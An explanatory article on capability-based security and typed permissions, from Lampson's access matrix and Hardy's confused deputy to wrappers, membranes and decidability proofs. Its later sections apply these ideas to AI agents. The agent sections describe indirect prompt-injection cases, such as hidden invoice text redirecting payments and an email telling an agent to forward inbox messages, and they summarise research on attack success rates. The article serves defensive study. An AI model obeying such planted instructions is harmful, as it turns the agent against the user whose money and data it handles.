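# Capability-based security and typed permissions for controlling what code can do

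## Background: programs, permissions and tool calls

In capability-based security, a program can use a resource, such as a file, a network connection or a payment service, only if it holds a capability for it. A capability is an unforgeable reference that names the resource and permits its use. With typed permissions, the programming language's type system records which capabilities each piece of code may use, and the compiler rejects code that goes beyond them before the program runs. Researchers first built capabilities into operating systems in the 1960s and 1970s, and later into programming languages. More recently, they have applied the same ideas to AI agents, which write programs and run them on people's behalf.

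On most computers, the operating system usually runs a program with all the powers of the user account that started it. Suppose Alice opens a text editor to correct a letter. The editor only needs to read and write that one file, but it can also read her tax returns, overwrite her photographs and delete every file she owns, because the operating system treats whatever the editor does as something Alice does. If the editor's maker slipped in hostile code, or if a bug lets a malformed letter take control of the editor, the damage can extend to everything Alice can access. The operating system's protections would not prevent this even when working correctly, because Alice is allowed to delete her own files.

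The arrangement dates from a time when people sharing a computer worried mainly about each other. In *Protection*, Lampson (1971) wrote that protection mechanisms were originally meant to stop one user's malice or mistakes from harming another user. He observed that all the reasons for wanting protection are just as strong if one replaces "user" with "program". Ordinary file permissions still serve the original purpose of protecting users from each other, and do little to protect a user from the programs she runs, such as her text editor.

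### The access matrix

Lampson's paper also introduced what became the standard way of writing down who may do what. An access matrix is a table with a row for each subject (anything that can act, such as a user or a running program) and a column for each resource. Each cell lists the kinds of access that the subject has to the resource. Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003), in *Capability Myths Demolished*, give a small example with three users and three Unix files:

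| | /etc/passwd | /u/markm/foo | /etc/motd |
|---|---|---|---|
| Alice | read | write | none |
| Bob | read | none | read |
| Carol | read | write | read |

On a real system most of the cells would be empty, so storing the whole table is impractical. One alternative is to store each column with its resource, as an access-control list. For the file /u/markm/foo, this list is "Alice: write, Carol: write". The other is to store each row with its subject, as a capability list. Bob's list is "read /etc/passwd, read /etc/motd". When a subject tries to use a resource, a system with access-control lists establishes who is asking and looks for that name on the resource's list. With capability lists, the subject presents an entry from its own list, and the system only needs to check that the entry is genuine.

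Miller and colleagues argue that the two designs are not equivalent, although many people have concluded that they are because rows and columns contain the same facts. Their reason is that the matrix is a snapshot and leaves out the rules for changing its cells. Lampson did propose such rules. For instance, a subject with "owner" access to a file could add entries anywhere in that file's column, and a subject could copy one of its own entries to another subject only if the entry had a "copy flag". Most people remember the table without the rules. In the access-control systems that Miller and colleagues knew, permission to change one entry generally came with permission to edit the resource's entire list, whereas in capability systems each subject managed its own row. Two systems could therefore start with identical tables and permit quite different ones later.

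The choice between columns and rows also affects how finely a system can tell programs apart. An access-control list has to name its subjects, so whoever maintains the lists must keep track of which subjects exist. This is feasible for people with accounts, who come and go slowly, but very hard for running programs, which a computer starts and stops all the time. As Miller and colleagues explain, these systems therefore group running programs into broad classes, normally user accounts, so the system treats Alice's text editor as Alice. Administrators sometimes create a separate account for a particular program, but every running copy of that program then shares the account. With capabilities, each subject holds its own list, so nobody needs to keep a register of subjects, and each running copy can have its own row.

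### Ambient authority and least privilege

To open a file on Unix, a program calls open() with the file's name and the kind of access it wants. It presents no credential. The operating system checks whether the account running the program has permission for that access, then allows or refuses the call. This is ambient authority, which a program can use just by naming a resource, because of who is running it. Miller and colleagues compare it to a world where doors have no keys and simply open for anyone deemed worthy.

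Under ambient authority, a program only has to supply a file's name to open it. If the editor can construct the path to Alice's tax return, it can open the return. Anyone who can influence which names a program constructs can therefore influence which files it touches, even without having access to them.

*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) set out the principle of least privilege, that code and people should get only the access their task needs. The two main reasons it gave are that least privilege limits the damage from an accident or error, and that it reduces the number of programs somebody has to audit when a question of misuse arises. The editor breaks this principle because it needs one file and gets access to all of them. But following the principle with accounts and access-control lists would mean creating an account for each job and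 editing the permissions of each file involved, and few people would do that to correct a letter. The paper also set out a principle of "psychological acceptability", that a protection mechanism should be easy enough for people to apply routinely and correctly. Much of the difficulty is in satisfying both principles at once.

### Types and effects

A type describes the values that an expression can produce, and therefore which operations make sense on them. The number 7 has the type integer. A function that takes an invoice and returns a sum of money has the type Invoice → Money. Before a program runs, a type checker, usually part of the compiler, works out the type of each expression from the types of its parts. It rejects the program if it finds a mismatch, such as a date passed to a function that expects money. If the type system is sound, no program that passes can make this kind of error,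 whatever its input. Testing cannot guarantee this, because it covers only the inputs that somebody tried. However, the checker will accept a program that pays €9,400 instead of €940, because both are money. It also rejects some programs that would have run without trouble, because it has to decide without knowing the inputs.

Ordinary types also leave out effects, which are anything code does besides returning a value, such as writing a file or sending a message. In most widely used languages, the type checker treats two functions of type Invoice → Money as interchangeable even if one only returns the invoice's total and the other also emails the invoice to a stranger.

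### Agents, tool calls and prompt injection

An agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools. The model only produces text, and the ordinary software around it, called the harness, acts on some of that text. A tool call is a request to run an external service or function with certain arguments, such as an account number and an amount for a payment. When the model writes a tool call, the harness carries it out and adds the result to the text that the model reads before its next step. Some agents write a whole program, which the harness runs and which makes the tool calls itself. In either case the calls often use the user's credentials, so the agent is in roughly the same position as the text editor.

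Prompt injection is text planted in material an agent reads to make it act against its user's wishes. (This is the indirect form. In the direct form, the person typing to the model tries to override the developer's instructions.) The attack is possible because the model receives both the user's request and the contents of a stranger's email as text, with no firm boundary between instructions and data. The Frontier Model Forum's *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents*, a brief from an industry body, gives the example of an email with hidden instructions telling an agent to gather sensitive messages from the inbox and forward them to the attacker. The brief also points out that an injection that achieves little against an agent with a few narrow tools could lead to stolen data if the agent has broad access to files and stored passwords. It took a dishonest maker or a bug to turn the text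 editor against Alice, but a paragraph in a document an agent reads may be enough to turn the agent against its user.

In a hypothetical example, a small firm asks its agent to handle the month's bills. The agent writes a program that reads 40 supplier invoices from one folder, pays those due through a payment tool, and emails a summary to the accountant. One of the invoices contains a request, in white text on a white background, for payment to another account.

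The hidden line can affect the payments at two points. If the agent reads the invoices before writing the program, perhaps to learn their layouts, the line can influence the program itself. If the program uses a language model to extract the account number and amount from each invoice, the line can alter those values without changing the code. Code that extracted the figures by fixed rules and paid only accounts already on the firm's books would not be vulnerable to this attack. But forty suppliers may use forty layouts, which is a good reason to use a model.

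The task needs permission to read one folder, pay known suppliers the sums owed, and send one message to one address. If the harness runs the program under the bookkeeper's account, the program may be able to read every file the bookkeeper can read, pay anyone and message anyone. The Frontier Model Forum's brief repeats a warning, common among practitioners, about agents that combine access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. The invoice agent has to combine all three to do its job.

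### Training models to resist injection

Besides limiting tool calls, developers train models to disregard planted instructions. Training has made injection much harder, but it gives no guarantee. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tailored attacks to each of 12 published defences against prompt injection and related attacks. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences, although most of the defences' developers had originally reported rates near zero. For one model trained to resist injection, the success rate rose from 2% with a fixed set of attacks to 96% with tailored ones. The 2% figure was accurate for existing attacks, but a real attacker can study the defence first. Nasr and colleagues conclude that the most evaluators can do is try hard to break a defence and fail, which does not prove that the defence holds.

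*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* describes a public competition that Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) ran with several AI companies and government institutes. Like the dishonest supplier, the attackers controlled part of a single file, message or web page. The 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts on 13 leading models, and 8,648 succeeded. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% of attempts against Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% against Gemini 2.5 Pro. Participants could see the agent's conversation up to that point and knew exactly which action they had to trigger, so these rates are probably higher than a stranger would achieve in practice. But a supplier who knows that a customer pays its bills through an agent can guess a fair amount of this information.

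Newer models have been trained much more heavily to resist attacks. OpenAI trained GPT-5.6 against an automated attacker, using computing power on the scale of its largest training runs of this type. *GPT-Red* (Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues, 2026) describes the result as the company's most robust model up to then, but says that robustness "remains far from solved". Two months later, *Climbing the Hill* (Yin, Jin and colleagues, 2026) reported results for a new automated attack on two GPT-5.6 models against which two earlier ones had scored 0%. The new attack succeeded within ten tries in 94% of test cases on one model and 45% on the other.

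The best published figures are lower still. According to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection*, Anthropic recorded no successful attacks on Claude Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios, and a success rate of 2.0% after 15 attempts on a more general test, down from 5.5% for the previous model. This is real progress, and it may well be good enough for low-stakes tasks. But even if the 129 scenarios were a random sample of attacks, zero successes would be compatible with a true rate of up to about 2.3% at 95% confidence, and attackers do not choose at random. The failures are also not independent. Dziemian and colleagues found attack strategies that worked in 21 of their 41 scenarios and on several families of models, so a criminal who finds wording that works can put it on invoices to many firms.

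## A capability names a thing and permits its use

Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of MIT introduced the word "capability" in 1966, according to *Early Capability Architectures*, a chapter of Henry Levy's history of the field. They were designing a supervisor (the core of an operating system) for computers that ran many people's programs at once. In their design, each running computation has a list of capabilities. Each capability points to one object, such as an input device or a segment of memory (a file is a long-lived segment), and records what the computation may do with it. For a segment, it might permit reading, reading and writing, or only running it as code.

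A program in this design refers to an object by its position in the list. If it asks to write to entry 5, the supervisor looks up that entry in the program's list, follows the pointer and checks that the entry permits writing. If the entry does not exist or permits only reading, the supervisor suspends the program and alerts the program that set it up. Entry 5 in another program's list may point to a different object, so knowing the number gives another program no access. Programs cannot write entries into the list themselves, so they cannot forge a capability.

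### File names and open files

A file name, by contrast, only refers to a file. Anyone can write down or guess the name of Alice's tax return, but knowing the name doesn't give them permission to open the file, so that permission has to come from somewhere else.

*Paradigm Regained* (Miller and Shapiro, 2003) compares two Unix commands that both copy a file. With `cp foo.txt bar.txt`, the shell passes the two file names to cp as text, and cp opens the files itself. Since the user might type any name, cp needs permission to open every file the user can open. With `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the shell opens both files first and passes cat two open file handles. A handle is a small number that refers to an entry in a table the operating system keeps separately for each running program. On an ordinary system cat still runs with all the user's permissions, but it could do this job with only the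 two handles.

File handles, which Unix has always had, are therefore close to capabilities. One difference, according to Miller and colleagues, is that an access-control list governs the channel through which one running program sends a handle to another. In a pure capability system, a program would need a capability for that channel too.

Dennis and Van Horn kept readable names, but a program could look up a name only in a directory for which it held a capability. This did not automatically produce least privilege. When the supervisor started a computation for a user, it always put the user's main directory in the computation's capability list, which let the computation reach everything the user owned. A program could start another with a much shorter list, but someone had to choose to do so. Alice's text editor, started in the usual way, could still have reached her tax return.

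### Four ways to come to hold a reference

In the object-capability model, files, services and parts of programs are all objects, and they affect each other only by sending messages along references they hold. A message can carry further references. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) gives four ways an object can come to hold a reference. The firm that pays its bills through an agent could use all four.

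- By initial conditions: some references exist before the events that one wants to analyse. When the bookkeeper's request arrives, the harness already holds references to the firm's file store, bank connection and mail service.
- By parenthood: when one object creates another, it holds the only reference to the new object. The harness creates a payment object for each known supplier, which can pay that supplier's account and no other. At first only the harness can use these objects.
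- By endowment: a creator can give a new object some of the references that it holds itself. The harness creates the invoice program with references to the invoice folder, to the payment objects, and to a mail object that writes only to the accountant.
- By introduction: an object can send one reference along another. The invoice program keeps a record of its payments and passes it to an object that formats the summary. To do so, it has to hold references to both the record and the formatter.

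An object can drop references or rearrange the ones it has, but this never gives it a new one. Miller's slogan for this is "only connectivity begets connectivity". The invoice program, for instance, has no reference to the payroll folder, and could get one only from an object that holds one and can send the program messages, such as the harness. To find out whether this can happen, an auditor has to read the harness's code but can ignore the code the agent wrote.

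The model separates data from references. Numbers and text are data, and an object may have any data it can work out or receive. The hidden line on the invoice is text, so it can mention the payroll folder without giving the program a reference to it. But this protection depends on how the firm designs its objects. If the harness gave the program one payment object that accepted any account number as text, the account number would work like a file name. The dishonest supplier could write it on an invoice, and the payment object would provide the permission to pay that account.

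### The confused deputy

The best-known argument for capabilities comes from an accident around 1977 at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Hardy describes it in *The Confused Deputy* (1988) and calls his account "nearly true", with inessential details changed.

Tymshare kept its Fortran compiler in a system directory called SYSX. Users could give the compiler the name of a file for debugging output. The staff also had the compiler collect statistics on which language features people used and write them to a file called (SYSX)STAT. To allow this, they gave the compiler a "home files license", which let it write to any file in SYSX. That directory also contained the company's billing information, in a file called (SYSX)BILL.

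One user learned the name (SYSX)BILL and gave it to the compiler as the file for debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system in a request to open the file for writing. The operating system allowed the request because the compiler had a licence for SYSX. The compiler then wrote its debugging output over the billing information.

The compiler and the operating system had both worked as intended. The code that wrote the debugging output was correct when it was written, but in Hardy's view it became wrong when the staff granted the licence, although nobody had changed the code. To foresee the problem, the staff would have had to examine every place where the compiler wrote to a file. Hardy calls the compiler a confused deputy because it acted for both the user and the system's operators and had no way to tell the operating system which of them it was acting for.

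The argument from this case to capabilities has six steps:

1. A deputy has permissions from more than one source. The compiler could write to the user's files because the user ran it, and to SYSX because of its licence.
2. The caller chooses the target by name, and a name carries no permission.
3. The operating system allows a request if any of the deputy's permissions covers the target.
4. A caller can therefore direct the deputy to a target that the deputy may use and the caller may not.
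5. The deputy cannot reliably recognise such a request by examining the name.
6. If callers had to pass capabilities instead of names, they could point only to targets that they could use themselves, and the deputy would use the caller's permission to act on them.

The conclusion is that a system should join naming and permission in one reference. The first three steps describe Tymshare's system, the fourth follows from them, and the sixth follows from the definition of a capability. The fifth step remains to be examined, along with how many real attacks depend on a caller supplying a name.

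### Could the compiler check the user's rights?

Hardy considers three ways the compiler could refuse bad file names and finds problems with each. It could reject files in other people's directories, but users had good reasons to send output there. It could reject anything in SYSX, but that name did not exist when the compiler was written, and some users might have legitimate access to the directory. It could reject only (SYSX)BILL, but the directory contained other sensitive files, and somebody would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared.

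It would be better for the compiler to check with the operating system whether this user may write to this file. Tymshare did something similar by adding a "switch hats" system call, which let a program switch between its own licence and its caller's permissions. An attempt to open (SYSX)BILL with the caller's permissions would then fail, as it should. So the fifth step is too strong if it means no check could have worked.

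Hardy replies that the fix did not extend well. Some programs soon needed more than two sets of permissions, and the system used other mechanisms to control access to things besides files. The rules for opening a file had already grown to include 14 "ands" and "ors", and each new clause either opened a security hole in some program or broke one that worked. This is one engineer's experience with one system, and Hardy was by then senior architect at Key Logic, whose KeyKOS operating system was based on capabilities. He also reports that capability systems were usually smaller than equivalent systems with access lists, but he gives no figures.

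A stronger reason to prefer capabilities is that they limit the damage when a programmer makes a mistake. With hat-switching, a programmer who forgets to switch before opening the debugging file leaves the original vulnerability in place, though the program appears to work. With capabilities, the operators give the compiler a reference to (SYSX)STAT, and the user gives it a reference to an output file. Careless code might mix up the two and write debugging output over the statistics, but it could not touch the billing information, because neither reference leads there.

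### An injected agent may already hold what the attacker needs

An agent that follows a planted instruction is also a confused deputy. *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), a blog post by the security company Semgrep, describes how an agent connected to several tool servers collects permissions from all of them, so a line in an email can set off a command on the user's computer. The post proposes giving agents capabilities for one task at a time. In its example, a user asks for a summary of quarterly reports, and the agent gets a capability to read one folder for five minutes. One of the reports contains an instruction to delete all files. The agent tries to obey, but the server refuses because the agent has no capability to delete files.

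The refusal in this example does not depend on the model recognising the attack, which is an advantage over training. But the post's promise of "no confused deputies" goes too far. Miller and colleagues claim only that removing ambient authority makes it possible to write deputies that nobody can confuse. The programmer still has to keep track of what each capability is for. They compare a careless deputy to someone with a ring of keys who tries each one until the door opens.

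The invoice agent has to make payments, so an attacker can do harm using only the capabilities the agent already has. The hidden line might give the sum due as €9,400 instead of €940, or falsely list last month's bill as unpaid. The model chooses which of its capabilities fits the supplier's text, and the harness makes the call. The model then acts like Tymshare's operating system, which matched a name from one party to a permission that belonged to another. The sixth step of the argument assumes that callers pass capabilities, but a supplier who sends an invoice passes only text. The argument therefore gives no assurance about which of its capabilities the agent will use, or how.

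Capabilities can still reduce the damage. The harness could create a separate small program for each invoice and give it references only to that invoice and to the payment object for the supplier who sent it. A hidden line in the invoice could then affect only that supplier's payment. It could not send the money to a new account or reveal what other suppliers charge. This works only if the harness identifies the supplier by something other than the invoice's text, such as the address the invoice came from. An attacker could also still change the amount, since a payment object that accepts €940 will also accept €9,400 unless it has a limit.

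Rajani, Garg and Rezk formally established the general limit in 2016. *Full Provenance on the COSS Causal Axis* (Gallo, 2026) reports that they showed capabilities stop an attacker from explicitly designating a forbidden target, but do not stop every attack through values, control flow or the program's initial state. In the invoice example, a false amount is an attack through a value. Text that persuades the agent to pay twice is an attack through control flow, because it affects whether the program makes a call. A false entry already in the supplier register when the program started would be an attack through its initial state.

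Some newer work defines the problem by its cause, whether or not the attacker names a target. *Proof-of-Continuity* (2026) defines a confused deputy by four conditions: the user lacks a permission, the deputy has it, the user sends the deputy a request, and the request causes the deputy to use the permission. Hardy's compiler meets all four when it overwrites the billing file, but also whenever it records statistics, because users had no permission to write to (SYSX)STAT and running the compiler caused it to write there. People use deputies largely to do things they cannot do themselves, so a workable definition has to separate proper uses of the deputy's permission from improper ones.

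Gallo's model does this through explicit exceptions. Each event *e* in a program's history has a set of permissions *C(e)*. If *e* results from two earlier events *p* and *q*, then ordinarily

*C(e)* ⊆ *C(p)* ∩ *C(q)*,

which means that *e* may use only permissions that *p* and *q* both carry. Gallo proves that under this rule a request cannot lead to an effect that the request itself did not permit, provided that the system records every relevant cause and checks every protected effect. Suppose that the bookkeeper's request permits payments to suppliers, and that an incoming invoice permits nothing. The two sets have nothing in common, so the agent could not pay any amount that it had read from an invoice. To get its bills paid, the firm would have to authorise that combination as an exception, and the terms of the exception would determine how much a dishonest supplier could gain.

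### Are access lists and capabilities equivalent?

Much of the case for capabilities depends on their doing things that access-control lists cannot. Miller and colleagues accept that both can record the same access matrix at any one moment, which is why so many people think they are equivalent. The security researcher David Wagner said on record that he had thought the two roughly equivalent in expressiveness until Miller or one of his colleagues convinced him otherwise.

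The rebuttal relies on the direction of the references, as well as the rules for changing the table and the difficulty of listing every running program. An access-control list belongs to a file and refers to users, so a program needs a separate way to refer to the file, usually a name. That name cannot carry permission because the permission is kept with the file. A capability belongs to the program and refers to the file, so a single reference can both identify the file and permit its use.

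Storing the matrix by rows is not enough to achieve this. If Tymshare had kept a row for each program, the compiler's row would have included write access to everything in SYSX. If the operating system had searched that row for a permission to match the name (SYSX)BILL, it would have found one, and the accident would have happened anyway. A Unix mechanism called "POSIX capabilities" has the same weakness and is a form of ambient authority, despite its name. It gives a running program a fixed set of powers, such as changing the ownership of any file on the system, and the program does not choose which power to use for a given request.

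Miller and colleagues therefore compare four models, one of them based on the popular analogy between capabilities and keys:

| Model | Does referring to a resource always bring permission to use it? | Must a program choose which permission to use? | Must a program hold a reference to another program to pass it access? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Access-control lists | no | no | unspecified |
| Capabilities as rows of the matrix | unspecified | no | unspecified |
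| Capabilities as keys | no | yes | no |
| Object capabilities | yes | yes | yes |

If capabilities work like keys, a caller can still name a resource and leave the deputy to find a capability that permits its use. Only object capabilities prevent this. The requirement in the last column also makes it possible to stop a program from passing its access to others. Miller notes that Lampson's description of capabilities omitted this requirement.

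Some of the contrasts are less absolute than the table suggests. Miller and colleagues compare object capabilities with access-list systems as they found them, but Tymshare's hat-switching shows that designers can add a choice of permissions to such a system. On a cryptography mailing list in 2015, Jerry Leichter praised the paper but said that it "cheats a bit" by answering objections to capabilities with extensions to the capability model. His complaint does little to weaken the point about names, because that point follows from where each system keeps its references.

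An advantage of access lists is that an administrator can see which accounts may open a file by reading the file's list. With capabilities, the same information is spread across the lists of every running program. A lecture at Purdue University presents the confused deputy as a problem that capabilities can resolve, but then raises the question of how one user would share files with another. Dennis and Van Horn let an owner either mark a file as free for everyone or provide a routine that checked who was asking and then handed over a capability. The routine might well consult a list of approved users, so a capability system may still need access lists to decide who receives a capability.

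## Permission and authority: what code may do and what it can bring about

A program's permission is what it may do directly with the references it holds now. Its authority is everything it can bring about, directly or through other programs. Miller illustrates the difference with the Unix password file. Alice may write to the file and Bob may not, but Bob can send messages to Alice, and she writes whatever text he asks for into the file. So Bob has authority to change the file without permission to write to it. His authority depends on his permission to talk to Alice, her permission to write to the file, and how she behaves. An access matrix records the two permissions but not her behaviour.

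The firm's invoice program could be in Bob's position. Suppose each payment object holds a reference to the firm's ledger and, for every payment, adds a line that includes a note the program supplies. The program has no reference to the ledger, but it can put text of its choosing there. An auditor who listed only the program's references would miss this.

An object can also have permission without authority. Koepe (2019), in *Object-Capability as a Means of Permission and Authority in Software Systems*, gives the example of an object that holds a reference to a counter but whose only method does nothing, so no call to it can change the counter. We can only conclude this if we know the object's code. The firm can't rely on such reasoning for a program that an agent has just written, so it should assume that the program may use every reference it holds.

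Miller and Shapiro point out that the principle of least privilege does not specify whether to minimise permission or authority. The two can differ greatly. If the harness makes the program reach the bank through an object that forwards every message unchanged, the program loses its permission to use the bank but keeps all its authority over the money.

### A wrapper that pays only listed suppliers

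In the object-capability model, a reference gives full and permanent access to the object it leads to. To hand on something weaker, a programmer writes a small object that holds the strong reference, and gives out a reference to the small object instead. This is attenuation. The following wrapper pays only suppliers in the firm's register:

```
function makePayer(bank, register):
    accounts = copy(register)      # supplier name -> account number
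    object payer:
        pay(supplier, amount):
            if supplier not in accounts: fail("not a listed supplier")
            bank.transfer(accounts[supplier], amount)
    return payer
```

The harness calls this function with its bank connection and gives the program only the payer. The program cannot reach the bank connection because the payer keeps it in a private variable and has no method that returns it. The wrapper copies the register so that nobody can add an account to its list by editing the original later.

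The wrapper prevents payments to anyone not on the supplier list, but it doesn't prevent false amounts or double payments. Because it accepts the supplier's name as text, a hidden line in one supplier's invoice could also trigger a payment to another supplier on the list, unless the firm runs a separate program for each invoice.

Only the people whose money is at stake have to rely on this wrapper, because a mistake in it can do no more harm than its one bank connection allows. If a firm could add such rules only by changing the operating system, a mistake in one rule could expose everyone who used the computer.

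### A forwarder that can be switched off

An owner may want to withdraw access later. Redell described a way to do this in 1974, which capability programmers call the caretaker pattern:

```
function makeForwarder(target):
    enabled = true
    object forwarder:
        on any message (verb, args):
            if not enabled: fail("switched off")
            return target.verb(args)
    object switch:
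        off(): enabled = false
    return forwarder, switch
```

The harness gives the program a forwarder for the invoice folder, keeps the switch, and turns the forwarder off when the month's bills are done. After that, every message to the forwarder fails. If the program has passed the forwarder to other objects, they lose access too, because they use the same forwarder. To cut off one holder and not another, the harness would have to make a separate forwarder for each.

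Switching off the forwarder doesn't undo anything the program has already done, and it may leave some access in place. Suppose the folder has an `open` method that returns a file object. The forwarder passes this object straight to the program, which can keep using the file after the harness switches off the forwarder. Miller warns that the pattern protects its user only if the target does not give its clients direct access to itself.

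### A membrane around everything that passes

A membrane closes this gap by wrapping every reference that crosses it, in either direction:

```
function makeMembrane(target):
    enabled = true
    function wrap(x):
        if x is data: return x
        object wrapper:
            on any message (verb, args):
                if not enabled: fail("switched off")
                return wrap(x.verb(wrap each of args))
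        return wrapper
    object switch:
        off(): enabled = false
    return wrap(target), switch
```

Now `open` returns a wrapped file. All the wrappers share one `enabled` variable, so setting it to false disables the folder and every file opened through it.

The membrane must also wrap arguments. Suppose the program passes the folder an object to call when new invoices arrive. If the folder received that object unwrapped, it could later send an unwrapped file through it, and the program would have a reference that the switch does not control. The membrane instead gives the folder a wrapper for the object and wraps any file the folder sends through it.

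Numbers and text cross the membrane unchanged because, Miller argues, data provides only knowledge, which nobody can take back. When the harness turns off the switch, the program still has the text of every invoice it has read and can send this text through any other capability it holds. Controlling that requires tracking data from one call to the next. The membrane also has no effect on other routes. If the program and the folder both have access to an object that stores references, they can exchange references through it.

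Miller describes this simple version as secure but not yet efficient enough for practical use. An object that crosses the membrane and comes back also picks up two wrappers, so the program may not recognise its own object.

### Bounding authority by reachability

Since messages travel only along references, an object can affect only what it can reach by following them. Two groups of objects with no references between them cannot affect each other, and the rules for gaining references ensure that they never become connected. If a few objects link the groups, everything that passes between them depends on those few. (Miller leaves aside covert channels, such as one program signalling to another by varying how busy it keeps the processor.)

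An auditor could try to work out a program's authority in three ways, which give successively looser answers:

actual authority ⊆ bound from references and known code ⊆ bound from references alone

Calculating a program's actual authority is intractable because it depends on how all the code will behave. An auditor can easily calculate an upper bound from references alone, by following them and assuming that every object along the way will do anything it is permitted to do. If this search doesn't reach the payroll folder, the auditor can be sure that the program will never affect it, but if the search does reach the folder, the program may or may not be able to affect it.

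The invoice program has a reference to the payer, which has a reference to the bank connection. An auditor who looks only at references has to assume that the payer might give the invoice program the bank connection, although the payer is meant to prevent that. To rule this out, the auditor has to read the payer's few lines of code but can still treat the invoice program as hostile. Miller recommends this intermediate approach, in which the auditor considers an object's behavior only if there is reason to rely on it.

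A list of permissions can't replace this analysis. In 1984, Karger and Herbert proposed giving a security officer a list of everyone with access to a compromised object. The list would omit a program that used the object through a forwarder. Such a list shows less about who can affect what as a firm becomes more careful to limit the permissions it grants.

### When an algorithm can decide who may gain access

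Researchers have also studied how hard the question is in general. Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman (1976), in *Protection in Operating Systems*, modelled a protection system as an access matrix with a fixed set of commands for changing it. A command checks that certain rights are present in certain cells. If they are, it carries out a list of steps, each of which adds or deletes a right, or creates or destroys a subject or an object. For example, this command lets the owner of a file give someone else permission to read it:

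```
command CONFER_READ(owner, friend, file)
    if own in (owner, file)
    then enter read into (friend, file)
```

A starting access matrix is "safe" for a right if no sequence of commands can put that right into a cell that lacked it. An owner can nearly always grant access to others, so "Protection in Operating Systems" recommends removing trusted subjects from the matrix before checking whether it is safe.

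Harrison and colleagues proved that no algorithm can answer this question for every system. They proved this by showing that a protection system can imitate any Turing machine, a simple mathematical model of a computer with a tape, a head that reads and writes one cell of the tape at a time, and an internal state. Each tape cell is represented by a subject that owns the subject for the next cell, which keeps the cells in order. If a cell contains the symbol X, its subject has a right called X over itself. The subject under the head also has a right that represents the machine's state. Each command carries out one move of the machine by checking for the old symbol and state and replacing them with the new ones. If the head moves past the last cell, the command also creates a new subject.

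The matrix then leaks the right for the machine's final state exactly when the machine reaches that state. Mathematicians already knew that no algorithm can predict this for every machine, so none can decide safety for every protection system. Harrison and colleagues also showed that for one particular system with fixed commands, no algorithm can decide the safety of every starting matrix.

The problem becomes decidable if each command may perform only one step. With *g* kinds of right, *S*₀ starting subjects and *O*₀ starting objects, the shortest sequence leading to a leak then has at most

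*g*(|*S*₀| + 1)(|*O*₀| + 1) + 1

commands. For a matrix with three users, three files and two rights, the limit is 57, because users also count as objects. But this restriction is unrealistic. A one-step command cannot even create a file and make its creator the owner. If commands can take several steps but cannot create anything, safety is again decidable, although probably only in exponential time.

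Lipton and Snyder (1977), in *A linear time algorithm for deciding subject security*, gave a much faster answer for a different model, called take-grant. Bishop (1988), in *The Sharing of Rights and Information in a Capability-Based Protection System*, sets out its rules. The model represents a system as a graph whose arrows carry rights. Only subjects can act, and they have four rules:

- Take: if *x* has the take right over *y*, then *x* can acquire any right that *y* holds.
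- Grant: if *x* has the grant right over *y*, then *x* can give *y* any right that *x* holds.
- Create: *x* can create something new and have any rights over it.
- Remove: *x* can give up rights that it holds.

These rules let two cooperating programs pass rights in either direction, even when only one has the take right over the other. Suppose a supervisor program has the take right over a worker program, and the worker has no rights over the supervisor. The worker can create a box over which it has take and grant rights. The supervisor takes the grant right over the box from the worker and uses it to put its own right to the payroll file in the box. The worker then takes the payroll right from the box.

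One party can therefore gain a right over a file if and only if, in the starting graph, somebody already has that right and a suitable chain of take and grant arrows connects the two parties. An algorithm can check this in time proportional to the size of the graph, even if subjects can create any number of new things.

The two results differ because the model of Harrison and colleagues lets a designer write any commands, including ones that use rights as symbols in a calculation, while take-grant's rules are fixed and treat all rights alike. In take-grant, a new vertex starts out connected only to its creator, so creating vertices cannot join parts of the graph that had no connection. Bishop attributes the quick answer to take-grant's commands being one-step, but they are not one-step by the 1976 paper's definition, since the create rule both makes a new vertex and adds rights over it. Bishop's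 proof still holds because it relies on paths in the graph, not on the commands being one-step.

Fixed rules also limit which policies a designer can express. A command in the 1976 model could require approval from both the bookkeeper and the director before a program received the right to make payments. None of the four take-grant rules can impose such a condition.

According to Miller, people often misread the 1976 result as showing that safety is never decidable. Harrison and colleagues said explicitly that it only means designers must consider restricted or individual cases. Object-capability systems have fixed rules for gaining references, so simple reachability arguments work for them.

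However, the linear-time analysis assumes that every subject, including the payer, may help to cause a leak, so its result is that the invoice program might get the bank connection. If the auditor followed the advice to remove trusted subjects and took the payer out of the graph, the answer would be "no". That answer is correct for permission, but it leaves out the program's authority to pay suppliers through the payer.

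### Boebert's argument that secrets can flow downward

In 1984, Boebert argued that an unmodified capability machine cannot enforce military secrecy rules. These rules let a program read only material at or below its clearance and write only to places at or above it. The restriction on writing, known as the *-property, prevents a program that has read a secret from copying it to where programs with lower clearance can read it.

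Miller and colleagues reconstruct the argument with a low-level program, a high-level program and a memory segment at each level. The machine hands out capabilities in accordance with the rules. The low-level program can read and write the low segment, and the high-level program can read it but not write to it. The attack has three steps:

1. The low-level program stores its capability to write to the low segment in the low segment itself.
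2. The high-level program reads that capability from the segment.
3. The high-level program reads a secret from the high segment and uses its new capability to write it to the low one.

Miller and colleagues accept that the attack works on the machine Boebert described, but they object that this machine, unlike most capability systems, lets programs send capabilities wherever they can send data. In KeyKOS, for instance, reading data from a segment and reading capabilities from it are separate operations with separate permissions. If the high-level program may read only data from the low segment, the attack's second step fails. Miller and colleagues also cite a formal verification that a system with independent controls on the two kinds of transfer can enforce the *-property.

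The argument still applies to systems in which a capability is just a hard-to-guess string of bits. Anyone who can send text can send such a string, unless the designers have added another defence. Boebert later described the 1984 paper as "no more than an offhand remark", but other researchers had been citing it for nearly two decades as proof of a general limit.

In another reply, Miller and Shapiro use a small program called a data diode. It consists of a variable shared by two objects, a writer that stores an integer in it and a reader that returns that integer. The low-level program gets the writer and the high-level program gets the reader. Data can then flow upward, but no capability can flow either way, because the writer accepts only integers. Going by references alone, Boebert would still seem to be right, since the diode might pass on any reference it received. One has to read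 its code to see that it can't. Neither reply deals with covert channels, which is a serious omission for people guarding military secrets, because a high-level program might still leak a secret through the timing of its actions.

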